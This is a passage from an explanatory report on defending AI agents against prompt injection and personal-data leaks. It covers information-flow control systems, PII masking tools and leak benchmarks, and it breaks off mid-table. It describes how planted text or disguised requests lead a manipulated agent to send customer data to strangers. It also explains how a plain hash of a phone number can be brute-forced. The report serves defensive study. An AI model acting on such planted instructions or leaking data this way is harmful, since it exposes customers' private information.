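The AgentDojo test simulated a fully manipulated model by inserting the attacker's tool call after the agent's first legitimate call. Attacks that sent out data or money succeeded 75–100% of the time without the system, depending on the type of attack, and never succeeded with it. A further check, which compares each action with the declared task, reduced the success rate of destructive attacks, such as deleting files, from 38.6% to 4.0%. For attacks that altered something, such as a calendar or a scheduled payment, the rate fell from 90.5% to 12.1%. Most of the attacks that still succeeded used the same action type as the user's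 own task. For example, if the user wants a calendar entry, a rule about action types can't exclude the attacker's entry.

Muruaga measured utility separately with Claude Sonnet 4.6, on 949 combinations of a user's task and an attack. Utility was 13.9 percentage points lower when the system refused every action that needed approval, and 8.6 points lower when a simulated person approved those actions. With those approvals, the agent completed as many travel tasks as before, but its completion rate on Slack tasks fell by 13 points. The checks took less than a millisecond.

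In a matched comparison with handwritten rules, Progent, which checks arguments against a policy, also stopped every attack, and its utility was 1.6 points higher. The AgentDojo results therefore don't show that a history check stops attacks that good argument constraints miss. A history check should help most when the agent needs to choose from a wide range of recipients and records, as it does for the complaints summary.

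The history also ends with the session. In one of Muruaga's attack tests, the agent read the data in one session and sent it in another, and the system allowed both. If the shop starts a new session for each ticket, a manipulated agent could save Maria Lopez's phone number in a note while handling her ticket, then email the note to a stranger while handling the next one. But with longer sessions, a reply to one customer could block every lookup for the rest of the day. Muruaga suggests a lasting record of where data has been, which would have to stay with the phone number after the session ended.

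### Tracking where data came from

Information-flow control attaches labels to data and carries them forward when a program copies or combines it. Costa, Köpf and colleagues (2025), in *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control*, apply the idea to agents in a system from Microsoft called FIDES. Each piece of data has one label for its origin, trusted or untrusted, and another for its secrecy, which can be a list of the people allowed to read it. If the agent makes *z* out of *x* and *y*, then *z* is untrusted when either source is, and its permitted readers are those the sources have in common:

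readers(*z*) = readers(*x*) ∩ readers(*y*)

The labels can't be attached precisely to what a model writes, because any word in its context might have influenced the answer. It is safest to treat everything the model writes after reading a stranger's email or ticket as untrusted, but that rule would block almost everything the agent tried to do after reading one.

In 2023, Willison proposed using two models to avoid this. A planning model decides which tools to use and doesn't see untrusted text. A quarantined model reads that text and answers questions about it, but has no tools. The planning model refers to each answer by a variable name, so it can pass the answer on without reading it.

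*Defeating Prompt Injections by Design* (Debenedetti and colleagues at Google DeepMind, 2025) presents CaMeL, which combines the two-model arrangement with labels. According to *CaMeLoT* (Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues, 2026), the planning model writes a short program from the user's request. An interpreter runs the program and labels each value with where it came from and who may read it. Before each tool call, a policy checks the labels and allows or refuses the call.

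The labels are necessary because separating the models protects only the plan. In one example, the plan is to read a channel's messages, find Bob's email address in them and send him a meeting time. Planted text can't add a step to the plan, but it can make the quarantined model return the attacker's address as Bob's. Since the label shows that the address came from the channel's messages, a policy can block its use as a recipient.

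Maria Lopez's phone number would pass through a system of this kind as follows:

1. The planning model reads the manager's request. Its plan is to fetch the tickets and customer records, have the quarantined model summarise them and email the summary to the consultant, whose address the manager has supplied.
2. The lookup tool returns Maria Lopez's record. The system labels her phone number as readable by the shop's staff and by her, and stores it in a variable. The planning model sees only the variable's name.
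3. The quarantined model reads the records and tickets, including the planted text, and puts her number in the summary. The system labels the summary as untrusted, because some of its sources are. Only the staff may read it, since they are the only readers all the sources share.
4. The agent calls the email tool. The consultant isn't on the summary's list of readers, so the enforcement point refuses the call.

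The refusal doesn't depend on anyone noticing the phone number. But the enforcement point would also refuse a harmless summary, because the label is based on the summary's sources rather than its text. Someone with the authority to release the summary would have to approve it before the shop could send it.

Costa and colleagues also describe a rule under which the decision to send and the recipient must be trusted, but the message needn't be. That rule would allow the agent to send the summary, including the phone number, because the manager did ask it to email the consultant. The rule prevents a stranger from choosing the recipient, but not from influencing the contents.

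FIDES can also limit how much a quarantined answer reveals. If the planning model only needs to know whether an email requests a meeting, the system can require a yes-or-no answer. An attacker can make the answer wrong, but one bit is unlikely to carry a usable instruction. Costa and colleagues left this feature out of their main test because most AgentDojo tasks didn't need it.

Even correct labels don't stop every leak. Suppose the agent sends a particular letter only to customers over 70. Anyone who learns that Maria Lopez received it can infer something about her age, although the letter doesn't mention it. Costa and colleagues prove that their method blocks direct copying of secret data, but it doesn't block inferences from which actions the agent takes. To block those too, the system would have to refuse almost any visible action after the agent had read something private.

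### What tracking costs

In Costa and colleagues' AgentDojo tests with gpt-4o, an ordinary agent carried out 152 attacks. FIDES carried out 21 when the researchers switched off its policy checks, because the planning model could choose to open a variable and read the planted text. With the checks on, it carried out none. The benchmark counted three successes, but the researchers examined them and found that no attacker had got anything the policies forbid.

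The same checks also stopped every attack on an ordinary agent without variables. Hiding text in variables mainly helps the agent complete its tasks under the checks, as the utility figures for tasks without an attack show.

| AgentDojo part | Ordinary agent, no checks | Ordinary agent with checks | FIDES with checks |
|---|---|---|---|
| Workspace | 75.0% | 37.0% | 59.0% |
| Travel | 70.0% | 73.0% | 41.0% |
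| Banking | 98.8% | 37.5% | 52.5% |
| Slack | 93.3% | 20.0% | 47.6% |

FIDES recovered part of the loss in every area except travel, where gpt-4o often struggled to use the variables. With OpenAI's o1, a stronger reasoning model, FIDES completed 68% of the travel tasks. Both models are now old, and a newer model would probably handle the variables better.

Even a stronger model can't complete every task under the policy. Some banking tasks ask the agent to open a file and follow the instructions in it, which the policy is meant to prevent. CaMeL is even stricter, since its plan can't change in response to what the tools return. In FIDES, the planning model can open a variable and adapt, but the system then treats its later decisions as untrusted.

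Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues (2026), in *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy*, report a loss in task completion of up to 30% on AgentDojo for systems such as FIDES and CaMeL. The group, which includes several FIDES researchers, argues that this comparison is unfair because many real agents ask a person before doing anything consequential. An agent without information-flow control should therefore also be judged by what it can do alone. By that measure, an ordinary agent using OpenAI's o3-mini completed 24.3% of tasks without needing approval, compared with 50.1% for FIDES.

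Their own version, PRUDENTIA, gives the planning model the labels and policies so it can look for a plan that won't need approval. It completed 59.1% of tasks unaided. With o4-mini, it needed about half as many approvals as FIDES (19.2 versus 36.8 across all tasks) but completed slightly fewer tasks (73.2% versus 75.7%).

Part of the saving comes because PRUDENTIA can ask the user to vouch once for an email that contains ten things to do, instead of asking for approval of each action. But a user who vouches for an email without noticing the planted text in it removes the restriction on what the agent does next. Kolluri and colleagues assumed that people would catch malicious requests, so their results don't show how often users would make this mistake.

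### Rules about the whole plan

CaMeL's policies check one call at a time, using the labels on its arguments, so they have no natural way to express a requirement such as "every incident the agent opens must eventually be closed". Nikolaou and colleagues add a check on the complete plan before any tool runs. Their system converts the plan into a map of its possible steps, then uses a program called a model checker to search every route through the map for one that breaks a rule.

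The shop could use this to require a person's approval before any email containing customer data leaves the company. If the plan had no approval step, the model checker would return the path that breaks this rule, and the planning model could add the step. A runtime check might find the problem only after the agent had read thousands of tickets. But a check made in advance doesn't have access to the actual values, so CaMeL's own policies still have to run. The advance check may also reject safe plans, because it treats a loop as able to repeat any number of times.

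*Operationalizing CaMeL* (2025) warns that features of Python, the language CaMeL's plans are written in, make this kind of analysis difficult and prevent strong guarantees about information flow. Nikolaou and colleagues rely on CaMeL accepting only a restricted version of Python, which leaves out some of the hardest constructs to analyse.

### Leaks that need no planted instruction

Someone who asks an agent for information can also obtain it without hiding instructions in the agent's data. *Confuse the Model, Control the Flow* (Shim, Karim and colleagues, 2026) tested three ways of doing this. In the paper's example, Jane's agent has access to Mark's diagnosis, and his ex-wife Emily wants to learn it.

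- Emily creates a shared page and invites the agent to fill in its part, so the disclosure looks like ordinary teamwork.
- Emily lists true and false statements about Mark and asks the agent to delete the wrong ones. The statements it leaves are the true ones.
- Emily asks by email for a one-word reply, while a shared page asks for the details. The agent may not connect the two.

One defence tested was a detailed prompt telling the agent to verify identities and wait for consent. With DeepSeek-V3.2 as the agent, these attacks still extracted 52.2%, 75.6% and 43.8% of the sensitive items, respectively. The agent could apply the instructions only when it recognised a request for information, and the attacks disguised their requests.

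Shim and colleagues' system, FlowSeal, labels records by owner and tracks which ones the agent has read. Code outside the agent intercepts every attempt to write or share something. If the recipient is neither approved nor blocked, a separate model compares the proposed message with those records and returns only "safe" or "blocked". FlowSeal reduced the leaks to 0.5%, 2.3% and 2.2%. In a smaller test with real Gmail and Notion accounts, the deletion trick extracted 34.7% of the items from an agent with an existing privacy defence and none from one with FlowSeal.

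FlowSeal could let a harmless complaints summary through and block one containing phone numbers, which labels alone can't do. But its guarantee is weaker, because Shim and colleagues' proof that protected data can't reach an unapproved recipient assumes the checking model makes no mistakes. They also excluded prompt injection from their tests. The checking model reads the proposed message, so text planted in it might cause the model to answer "safe".

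The paper incorrectly describes FIDES as leaving enforcement to the language model. In FIDES, ordinary code checks the labels before each tool call. The paper doesn't test FIDES or CaMeL, so its results don't show which approach works better.

On requests that involved no sensitive data, FlowSeal's utility was 72.4%, close to the 75.9% of the best prompt-based defence. It added about 1.7 cents to each run and increased running time by 37%. Its larger drawback was that the agent shared less data when sharing was appropriate. In a test where the data's owner would have agreed if asked, the agent with FlowSeal shared 32.7% of the requested items, compared with 61.0–85.6% for agents with the other defences. It asked for consent less often, so some people with a legitimate request never received an answer.

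## How is personal data hidden from the model while the agent still uses it?

The controls described so far limit which records an agent can fetch and where their contents can go. Once the support agent opens Maria Lopez's record, though, the model reads her phone number, and any outside company that runs the model receives it too. To hide the number and still let the agent use it, software has to find it, replace it and restore it when a tool or a person needs it.

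### Where data enters and where software can mask it

Personal data gets into the agent's context in four ways. A support worker may type it, for example by asking what happened to Maria Lopez's refund. Tools return it when the agent opens her ticket or customer record. A search of old complaints may return documents that name other customers. The agent's memory may also contain details from tickets it finished weeks ago.

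Masking one of these routes leaves the others open. LangChain's *PIIMiddleware* documents a masking component in a popular library for building agents. By default, the component checks the user's messages but not the results of tool calls. If the shop kept that setting, the component would check the worker's request but let the whole customer record through. Its built-in detectors cover email addresses, card numbers and several kinds of web and network address. The developer has to supply detectors for names and phone numbers.

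The shop can put masking software in three places:

- The client handles messages, tool results and tool calls, so it can mask data on the way to the model and restore it on the way to a tool.
- A gateway is a program that all the company's requests to models pass through. One gateway can cover many applications, including those whose developers never thought about masking.
- A tool server can mask a record before returning it. Glama, a directory of MCP servers, lists a plugin that does this with Presidio, an open-source masking tool that began at Microsoft. The client and its logs then never hold the real values, but a separate email server can't use Maria Lopez's address unless the two servers share a mapping table.

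Where the detector runs also matters. In *SurrogateShield*, Jathanna (2026) objects to cloud services that detect personal data, because the customer has to send them the unmasked text.

Some masking protects only the logs. LiteLLM's *PII, PHI Masking* describes a gateway that masks data using Presidio. In `pre_call` mode, it masks a message before sending it to the model. In `logging_only` mode, the model receives "Hi, my name is Jane!" unchanged, and only the stored copy has `<PERSON>` in place of the name. Langfuse, which makes software for recording what AI applications do, treats masking for the model and masking for the logs as separate decisions, since a model may need data that the company shouldn't keep in its logs. Masking the logs helps if an intruder reads them later, but it doesn't hide anything from the model or its provider, so a company buying a masking product needs to know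 which kind it is getting.

Software can also mask data between the model and its tools. *ToolMinimize* (Li, 2026) found that three now-old models put sensitive data the tool didn't need into 81–88% of their tool calls. Li's software rewrites the arguments of these calls, for instance by removing a value or making it more general. This protects the data from the tool's operator but not from the model, which has already read it.

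### How software finds personal data

The simplest detectors look for patterns. A regular expression is a formula for the shape of a piece of text, and experimental sample code from LangChain finds email addresses with this one:

```
\S+@\S+\.\S+
```

Here `\S+` means one or more characters that aren't spaces, and `\.` means a full stop. The pattern catches `maria.lopez@example.com` but misses `maria.lopez at example dot com`, which any support worker would recognise as an address. It also captures a comma directly after the address, because a comma isn't a space. The mapping table would then store the address with the comma, and the email tool might reject the restored address. The phone pattern in the same code requires hyphens, so it matches 212-555-0147 but not (212) 555-0147.

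A detector can check a possible payment card number with the Luhn test. It doubles every second digit, counting from the right, subtracts 9 from any result above 9, and adds the results to the remaining digits. The total must be a multiple of 10. For the test number 4111 1111 1111 1111, it is 30. A random 16-digit order number has a one in ten chance of passing, so the test removes about nine in ten of these false alarms. Presidio detects card numbers with a pattern and a checksum, according to Microsoft's *Supported entities*. Phone numbers have no checksum, so a detector must rely on their format and the words around them.

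Names don't have a fixed format, so systems find them with a named-entity recogniser, a model trained on text in which people have marked the names of persons, places and organisations. It learns to label names from their spelling and context, so it can recognise "Lopez" as a surname without a list of surnames. *A Comparative Study of Light-weight Language Models for PII Masking* (Acharya and Shrestha, 2025) lists nicknames, typos and words with several meanings among the difficulties. A place name may also have nothing to do with the user. Jathanna's system masks Wyoming in a sentence about someone who lives there, but leaves it in a question about the state's tax benefits.

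A token classifier does a similar job with labels designed for privacy. OpenAI (2026) released one called Privacy Filter, which is small enough to run on a laptop. It works like this:

1. The filter splits the text into tokens (word fragments).
2. It looks at the text on both sides of each token and gives a probability to each of 33 labels. One label means ordinary text. The other 32 combine eight categories, such as a private person or an account number, with four positions: the beginning, inside or end of an item, or an item that is a single token.
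3. It chooses the most probable sequence of labels that is valid as a whole. The end of a phone number can't come straight after ordinary text, for example, so the filter rules out any sequence containing that pair.

If each word in "Ben Morgan lives at" were one token, "Ben" would be labeled as the beginning of a person's name, "Morgan" as the end of it, and "lives" and "at" as ordinary text.

Because the filter uses context, it can recognise values that patterns miss. OpenAI's tests include a phone number spelled out in words and a web address with "[dot]" in place of each full stop. But the filter finds far fewer phone numbers when the surrounding text doesn't indicate what they are. An operator can adjust it to mask more text and miss less personal data, or the reverse.

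A general language model can also detect personal data. Anthropic's *PII purifier* is a prompt that tells the model to replace names, phone numbers and addresses with XXX, and warns that someone may have disguised them with spaces. This method needs no special training, and an operator can change the rules by editing the prompt. But the model writes the whole text out again, so it is slower and may alter words it should have left alone. If an outside company hosts the model, that company also receives the unmasked text. Acharya and Shrestha trained two smaller models that an operator could run itself. Both did about as well as leading models on a benchmark, but the one they tested on live chat messages did less well on informal writing.

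Many systems combine these methods. Jathanna's system applies patterns first, then a named-entity recogniser, then a second small model for doubtful cases. Some personal data still gets through. In Jathanna's worked example, a tenant called Sarah Chen asks for a letter to her landlord. The system replaces her name, address and social security number, but sends the landlord's name, Mr. Thompson, to the model unchanged. Jathanna counts only the tenant's three details as personal data and presents the example as one where no real personal data leaves the device.

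### Four ways to replace a value

Suppose the detector has found the name and address in "Maria Lopez wants a reply at maria.lopez@example.com." The table shows four replacements.

| Method | What the model reads | Can the shop recover the real values? |
|---|---|---|
| Deletion | wants a reply at . | No |
| Typed placeholder | [NAME_1] wants a reply at [EMAIL_1]. | Yes, with a mapping table |
| Realistic substitute | Helen Brooks wants a reply at h.brooks@example.net. | Yes, with a mapping table |
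| Keyed hash | name_7f3a91c2 wants a reply at email_c20b5e84. | Yes, with a mapping table or by hashing its customer list again |

Deletion reveals the least, but the model can't tell who wants the reply or where to send it.

A typed, numbered placeholder lets the model see what kind of value is missing and distinguish one person from another. The sample email in OpenAI's announcement of Privacy Filter uses placeholders without numbers, so the writer, Maya Chen, and the recipient, Jordan, both become [PRIVATE_PERSON]. If a model used that placeholder in a summary, the code that restores names couldn't determine which one to put back. The filter also masks the date of a product launch, which doesn't identify anyone.

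A realistic substitute keeps the sentence natural. However, if restoration fails, Helen Brooks looks like a real customer, while [NAME_1] is plainly a gap.

A hash function turns any text into a code of fixed length. The same text always gives the same code, and there is no practical way to run the function backwards. A keyed hash also mixes in a secret. Two departments that share the secret can use the codes to match their records of Maria Lopez without exchanging her name.

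According to Microsoft's *Presidio Anonymizer*, Presidio can delete a value, replace it, cover some of its characters, hash it or encrypt it. By default, it replaces the value with an unnumbered placeholder that names the type of data, such as `<PHONE_NUMBER>`. Covering some characters lets a support worker confirm the last four digits of a card. Encryption needs no mapping table, because anyone with the key can decrypt the value. But the encrypted name in Microsoft's example is a meaningless string of 44 characters, which the model would have to copy exactly. Decryption is Presidio's only built-in way to restore a value, so restoring placeholders takes extra software, such as LiteLLM's gateway, which can do this in the model's replies.

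### Why a plain hash of a phone number is weak

An attacker who can't run a hash function backwards can still run it forwards on every possible input and look for a match. A ten-digit phone number has

10¹⁰ = 10 billion

possible values. A machine that tests a billion a second gets through all of them in

10¹⁰ ÷ 10⁹ = 10 seconds

A shorter code doesn't help much. In LangChain's example of its hash option, the code has eight characters, each a digit or a letter from a to f, which allows 16⁸ or about 4.3 billion different codes. On average, 2.3 of the 10 billion phone numbers share each code, so the attacker can narrow each code to a few numbers.

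A keyed hash prevents this search if the key is long, random and secret, because the attacker can't compute the codes without it. AWS's *CRYPTOGRAPHIC_HASH* describes a data-preparation tool that keeps the key in a separate store for secrets. But an attacker can work out a weak secret from the codes. Mondoo's *CVE-2026-13455* records a flaw in PostgreSQL Anonymizer, a masking add-on for the database, which mixed a secret called a salt into each value before hashing it. Users who were supposed to see only masked data could call the hash function repeatedly, collect the results and work out the salt on their own machines. Version 3.1.2 fixed the flaw.

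Using a new secret salt for every value would also stop the search, but Maria Lopez's number would then have a different code in each document, so nobody could use the codes to match her records.

### Copying contact details without showing them to the model

Anthropic's *Code execution with MCP*, published in November 2025, shows how placeholders can work across two tool calls. In its example, a user wants to copy customers' contact details from a Google spreadsheet to Salesforce. Ordinarily, the model would read every row and copy each address and phone number into a call to Salesforce. In this design, the model writes a short program that makes the calls. The MCP client replaces the contact details with placeholders before they reach the model, then restores them in the call to Salesforce.

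Suppose the first row contains Maria Lopez's details. The table shows what each part of the system sees.

| Step | Model | MCP client | Spreadsheet tool | Salesforce tool |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| 1. The model writes the program | The request, the sheet's ID and the column names | Nothing yet | Nothing | Nothing |
| 2. The program fetches the sheet | Nothing new | The real details, which it stores in a mapping table beside [NAME_1], [EMAIL_1] and [PHONE_1] | The sheet's ID and the real rows | Nothing |
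| 3. The program prints the rows, if the model has told it to | Her Salesforce record ID and the three placeholders | Nothing new | Nothing | Nothing |
| 4. The program updates Salesforce | Nothing new | The record ID and the placeholders, which it exchanges for the real details | Nothing | The record ID and the real details |
| 5. The program reports that it has finished | The number of records updated | Nothing new | Nothing | Nothing |

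Anthropic's sample program skips step 3, so the model wouldn't see any contact details even without placeholders. The placeholders hide those details when the model does print the rows, perhaps to find out why an update failed.

The Salesforce record ID stays unmasked because the program needs it to update the right record. An outsider could learn little from it, but anyone with access to the company's Salesforce account could use it to find Maria Lopez.

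Anthropic describes the design but reports no test of the masking and doesn't explain how the client recognises personal data. A column headed "Email" is easy to mask, but a column of free-text notes needs one of the detectors described above. The placeholders can also break the program's logic. The lookup in step 4 implies that the program works with placeholders. If the user had asked to skip addresses at the shop's own domain, the program would skip none, because [EMAIL_1] doesn't contain a domain. The company using this design also has to run code written by a model, which Anthropic says requires a secure sandbox, resource limits and monitoring.

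The client can apply fixed rules about where data may go. For instance, it could replace [EMAIL_1] with the real address in calls to Salesforce, but not in calls to a tool that posts on a public website. Without such a rule, a manipulated agent could get the client to send the real address to the wrong recipient.

### SurrogateShield's substitutes

SurrogateShield uses realistic substitutes instead of placeholders. It runs on the user's computer, between a chat application and a hosted model. In the worked example, Sarah Chen becomes Ashley Wise, and her street address in Tempe, Arizona becomes one in Springfield, Washington. The model writes a letter signed Ashley Wise, and SurrogateShield puts the real name and address back before the user reads it. Substitutes have the right format, so a substitute card number passes the Luhn checksum test. Each substitute is unique within a session, except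 for expressions of gender, which come from a short list.

The mapping table never leaves the computer. SurrogateShield protects it in three steps:

1. It creates a random secret once and saves it in a file that only the user's account may read.
2. It combines the secret with each conversation's ID to make a separate key, so a thief who obtained one key couldn't open the other tables.
3. It encrypts the conversation's table with that key every time it saves it.

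Jathanna says this protects the tables if someone loses the device. But the secret is on the same disk as the tables, so a thief who could read the whole disk would have both. The protection therefore depends on the disk also being encrypted.

SurrogateShield also keeps two copies of each conversation, one with real values for the user and one with substitutes for the model. With a single copy, the real names restored in one reply would reach the model with the user's next message.

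Restoring the original data takes more than search and replace, because models don't always repeat a name exactly. SurrogateShield looks first for the full substitute, then for parts of it, such as "Ashley" alone, and finally for approximate matches. It looks for parts only when the full name hasn't appeared, since it might otherwise alter an unrelated mention of Ashley County. *PromptGraph* (2026) describes a stricter rule for placeholders. If the model has changed or invented one, the software leaves it alone, so the user may see an unfilled placeholder but not the wrong person's details. Russian surnames also change their endings according to their role in the sentence, and *Reversible Pseudonymisation of Documents Sent to External LLMs* (Beskorovainyi, 2026) found that a restoration tool sometimes produced the wrong form.

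The mapping table also has to last as long as the text that relies on it. If the shop deleted the table after each ticket, a note about [NAME_1] in the agent's memory could no longer be matched to a customer, and in the next session [NAME_1] might stand for someone else. SurrogateShield keeps a separate, permanent table for documents it has prepared for searching, so it can restore the names in those documents in any conversation.

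If a table's file becomes corrupted, SurrogateShield treats the table as empty and continues, so the user could receive a letter signed with the substitute name Ashley Wise. An unrestored substitute could do more harm in an agent. A call to an invented phone number might reach a stranger, whereas a call to [PHONE_1] would fail. Jathanna tested chat messages, not tool calls, so the results don't show how often this would happen.

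Jathanna's main evidence for substitutes is a measure of how closely a masked message resembles the original. Messages with substitutes scored 94.85%, and messages that Presidio had masked with placeholders scored 81.59%. A realistic name is almost certain to score higher on this measure than a label in brackets, and Jathanna acknowledges that the measure doesn't assess the model's answers. In another test, Claude Haiku tried to guess 196 hidden values from context. It recovered three from the messages with placeholders and none from those with substitutes, a difference that could be due to chance.

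### Tasks that need the real value

Some tasks need the characters that masking removes. A model that sees only placeholders can't check the spelling of "Lopez", put customers in alphabetical order or work out a region from a phone number. If identical values always get the same placeholder, the model can tell whether two addresses are the same, but not whether a difference between them is a typing error.

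A model given realistic substitutes may wrongly answer a question it couldn't have answered from placeholders. SurrogateShield replaces a date of birth with that of an invented person aged 18 to 80. A user who gives a date of birth and asks about pension eligibility could get a confident answer based on the wrong age.

Replacing an address with a fake one also causes a problem when the user asks about nearby places, since a list of pharmacies in Springfield is no use to someone in Tempe. For these questions, SurrogateShield changes the house number by between two and eight and leaves the rest of the address alone. The answer is then useful, but the model's provider learns which street the user asked about. SurrogateShield doesn't make this exception when the message mentions certain sensitive subjects, such as HIV, abortion or domestic violence.

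Ordinary code outside the model can do some of these jobs. It could run the Luhn test on a card number and return only whether the number passed, or compare the email address in Maria Lopez's ticket with the one in the shop's record and report that two letters are swapped. Somebody has to write that code before a customer asks the question. If no such code exists, the shop can let the model see one field for one task, such as her name but not her phone number, or pass the ticket to a person.

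## How often does masking miss something, and does the agent still do its job?

If the shop decides that the model may see a customer's name but not her phone number, the decision holds only when the detector finds the number. Three measures describe how well a detector works:

- Recall is the share of personal values in the text that the detector finds and hides.
- Precision is the share of the detector's masked fragments that really are personal data.
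- The document leak rate is the share of documents in which at least one personal value stays visible.

Suppose Maria Lopez's ticket begins "May I have a refund?" and contains her name, email address and phone number. The detector masks her name, her email address and the word "May", which it mistakes for a first name. It found two of the three personal values, so its recall is 67%. Two of the three fragments it masked are personal data, so its precision is also 67%. The ticket counts as a leak because the phone number is still unmasked.

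A detector could reach perfect recall by masking every word, so recall should be measured alongside precision. Low precision can also damage the documents an agent relies on. *RAGAL* (2026) describes a technical-support assistant at a government agency whose masking software mistook two common Romanian words for usernames. The software masked both words throughout the assistant's documents for eleven days, degrading about 3,000 passages, until one of them turned up in a search.

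### Why long documents leak

If a detector catches each value with probability *r*, independently of the others, the chance that it catches all *n* values in a document is *rⁿ*. The leak rate is therefore

1 − *rⁿ*

The table compares a ticket that contains three values with a document that contains 26.

| Recall | Tickets that leak (3 values) | Documents that leak (26 values) |
|---|---|---|
| 95% | 14% | 74% |
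| 99% | 3% | 23% |
| 99.9% | 0.3% | 2.6% |

To keep the leak rate for the longer documents down to 2%, the detector needs

*r* = 0.98^(1/26) ≈ 0.9992

or a recall of about 99.92%. A detector with 99% recall misses more than ten times as many values as that.

Real misses cluster within documents rather than occurring independently. A detector that fails on an unusual surname will probably fail on it again later in the document, and a badly typed document causes several misses. As a result, fewer documents leak than the formula predicts, but each leaking document reveals more.

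An agent makes the problem worse because it keeps adding text to its context. If the manager's complaints summary draws on 500 tickets with three values each, the detector has to mask 1,500 values. It would leave about 15 of them visible at 99% recall, and about one at 99.92%.

### A benchmark on whole documents

In October 2026, Beskorovainyi tested masking tools on 1,000 synthetic documents in Russian and 1,000 in UK English. They included contracts, certificates, business letters, staff documents and medical discharge summaries. The Russian documents averaged about 30 values to hide, and the English ones about 26. The generating program made roughly four in ten documents untidy, with typing errors, double spaces or unusual number formats. Some identifiers in the untidy documents were spelled out in words, had dots between the digits or had one digit wrong.

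The test covered five open tools and a baseline that used only patterns and checksums. Presidio and OpenAI's Privacy Filter appeared earlier. The other three are GLiNER Guard Omni, a detection model for several kinds of personal data; pii-guard, which combines rules with a model trained on Russian; and Prompt Anonymizer, an English tool built on Presidio. Beskorovainyi also tested their own engine, pii-roundtrip, which adds rules to pii-guard and GLiNER Guard.

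| Tool | Russian documents with a leak | UK documents with a leak | UK identifiers hidden | UK names, addresses and organisations hidden |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| pii-roundtrip | 0.3% | 0.2% | 100% | 99.98% |
| pii-guard | 60.8% | Russian only | Russian only | Russian only |
| GLiNER Guard Omni | 99.6% | 58.3% | 95.4% | 88.9% |
| Presidio | 87.1% | 61.1% | 92.5% | 58.5% |
| Privacy Filter | 97.0% | 81.1% | 95.7% | 84.4% |
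| Prompt Anonymizer | English only | 100% | 68.1% | 51.5% |
| Patterns only | 100% | 100% | 90.7% | 0% |

The best existing tools left a whole value visible in 61% of the Russian documents and 58% of the UK ones. These figures count an address or organisation as leaked only if all of it remains visible, so a tool that hides a postcode but leaves the town passes. When partly hidden values also count as leaks, the existing tools failed on 83.5% to 100% of documents, and Presidio's failure rate on UK documents rose from 61.1% to 100%.

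GLiNER Guard's results allow a rough check of the formula. The UK documents averaged about 12.6 identifiers and 13.2 names, addresses and organisations. At the recall rates in the table, if misses were independent, 88% of documents would have something left at least partly visible. The stricter count was 83.5%, so the misses clustered slightly.

Length explains part of the gap between these results and a tool's usual scores. pii-guard leaked in only 0.7% of a set of Russian texts averaging about 90 characters, compared with 60.8% of the longer documents. Some of that difference arises because the short texts contained no organisations, a type pii-guard doesn't support. Without organisations, its leak rate on the documents falls to 31.5%. Untidy text also matters, as GLiNER Guard leaked in 38.3% of the tidy UK documents and 86.0% of the untidy ones.

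A tool's score also depends on where the test data comes from. GLiNER Guard found 87.1% of identifiers in a Russian dataset from its developers and 70.8% in one from another group. Beskorovainyi therefore never judged an existing tool on its developers' dataset.

Beskorovainyi's engine, pii-roundtrip, does well largely because it treats the document as a whole. Once it has found a name, it masks every other mention of it, whereas GLiNER Guard might mask a full name at the top of a letter and miss a shorter form in the signature. But an early version of pii-roundtrip gave people with the same surname the same placeholder, which turned a landlord and a tenant into one person. Beskorovainyi considers this error worse than a leak, because a user is unlikely to notice it.

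The engine's 0.3% and 0.2% probably make it look better than it is. Beskorovainyi built the engine, designed the benchmark and ran it. All the documents were synthetic. The final ones were new, but they came from the same generator as six earlier sets that had guided the engine's development. The engine and the generator also share the code for checksums, which makes the perfect score on identifiers close to circular, as Beskorovainyi acknowledges. However, Beskorovainyi published the final documents and the rules for judging them before running any tool, and promised to publish the result whatever it was.

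Results on other people's data suggest how much worse the engine might perform elsewhere. On Nvidia's UK texts, which are also synthetic, it leaked in 0.9% of cases, although these texts averaged only 2.7 relevant values each. It hid 98.3% of the names, addresses and organisations. At that rate, if a document had 13 such values, there would be about a 20% chance that at least one stayed fully or partly visible. Mistakes in Nvidia's labels may explain some of the misses, but GLiNER Guard was trained partly on this dataset, which should have improved the engine's results.

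### Do placeholders survive the model's answer?

A hidden value is useful only if the software can put it back. To test whether it can, Beskorovainyi had two small models, Qwen 3.5 9B and Gemma 4 12B, write a summary and a reply letter from each of 190 masked documents per language. The software then replaced the placeholders with the original values in the resulting 380 answers per model in each language.

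In English, one placeholder failed in 760 answers. The models had altered 65 placeholders, for instance by dropping a bracket, but the engine's restorer accepts small changes. A stricter restorer can lose a lot of data because of such changes. In an earlier round with pii-guard's own placeholders, which look like web-page tags, Gemma left out the closing slash in 29 tags in one answer. The tool's restorer recognised none of them, while a more tolerant one recovered all 29.

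Russian names were harder to restore. With the worse of the two models, the engine correctly restored 94.6% of name placeholders, short of its 99% target, and about a quarter of the Russian answers contained at least one wrong name. Most of the errors came not from the models but from the pii-guard component that the engine uses to choose each name's grammatical ending. It often produced a wrong form, such as the plural "Kharitony" for the surname Kharitonov.

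Of the 289 failures in both languages, 188 came from this component. Another 82 happened because the engine had stored the name wrongly, for example as "Timofya" instead of "Timofey". Grammatical endings matter less in a tool call, where software can insert the stored name unchanged. But a wrongly stored name could make a customer lookup fail.

Models also drop placeholders and invent new ones. With pii-guard's own instructions, Qwen used no placeholders in 25 of 40 answers and either described the people in words or left them out. Restoration rates don't count these omissions, because there was nothing to restore. In the final test, Qwen invented 106 placeholders across both languages, while Gemma invented none. Many of the saved examples were [ORG_2], in replies that mentioned an organisation the document never named. Software can't restore an invented placeholder, so an agent's tool would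 receive the label itself as an argument.

The check confirms that the right value appears somewhere in the answer, but not that it appears in the right place. An agent could swap the sender and recipient of an email and still pass.

### How masking changes the answers

Masking personal data and restoring it in the output lowers the quality of ordinary writing only slightly. When GPT-4o wrote introductions, cover letters and business emails from masked prompts, the restored texts scored 9.37 out of 10, compared with 9.95 for texts written from the original prompts. Llama 3.3 70B's score fell from 9.76 to 8.41, so the average loss across the two models was about one point. Before restoration, both models' texts scored only a little above 3. GPT-4o graded all the texts, including its own, and both models are now old.

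Scores can fall much more on questions that depend on facts. Deußer, Hahnbück and colleagues (2026), in *On the Impact of Anonymization on the Performance of Large Language Models*, gave five models questions from eleven benchmarks, with and without numbered placeholders, and restored the real values before scoring the answers. The table shows four of the results for GPT-4o mini.

| Task | Original text | With placeholders |
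|---|---|---|
| Following instructions | 0.81 | 0.77 |
| Medical questions | 0.88 | 0.83 |
| Multi-step reasoning over long texts | 0.70 | 0.70 |
| Answering from retrieved documents | 0.80 | 0.32 |

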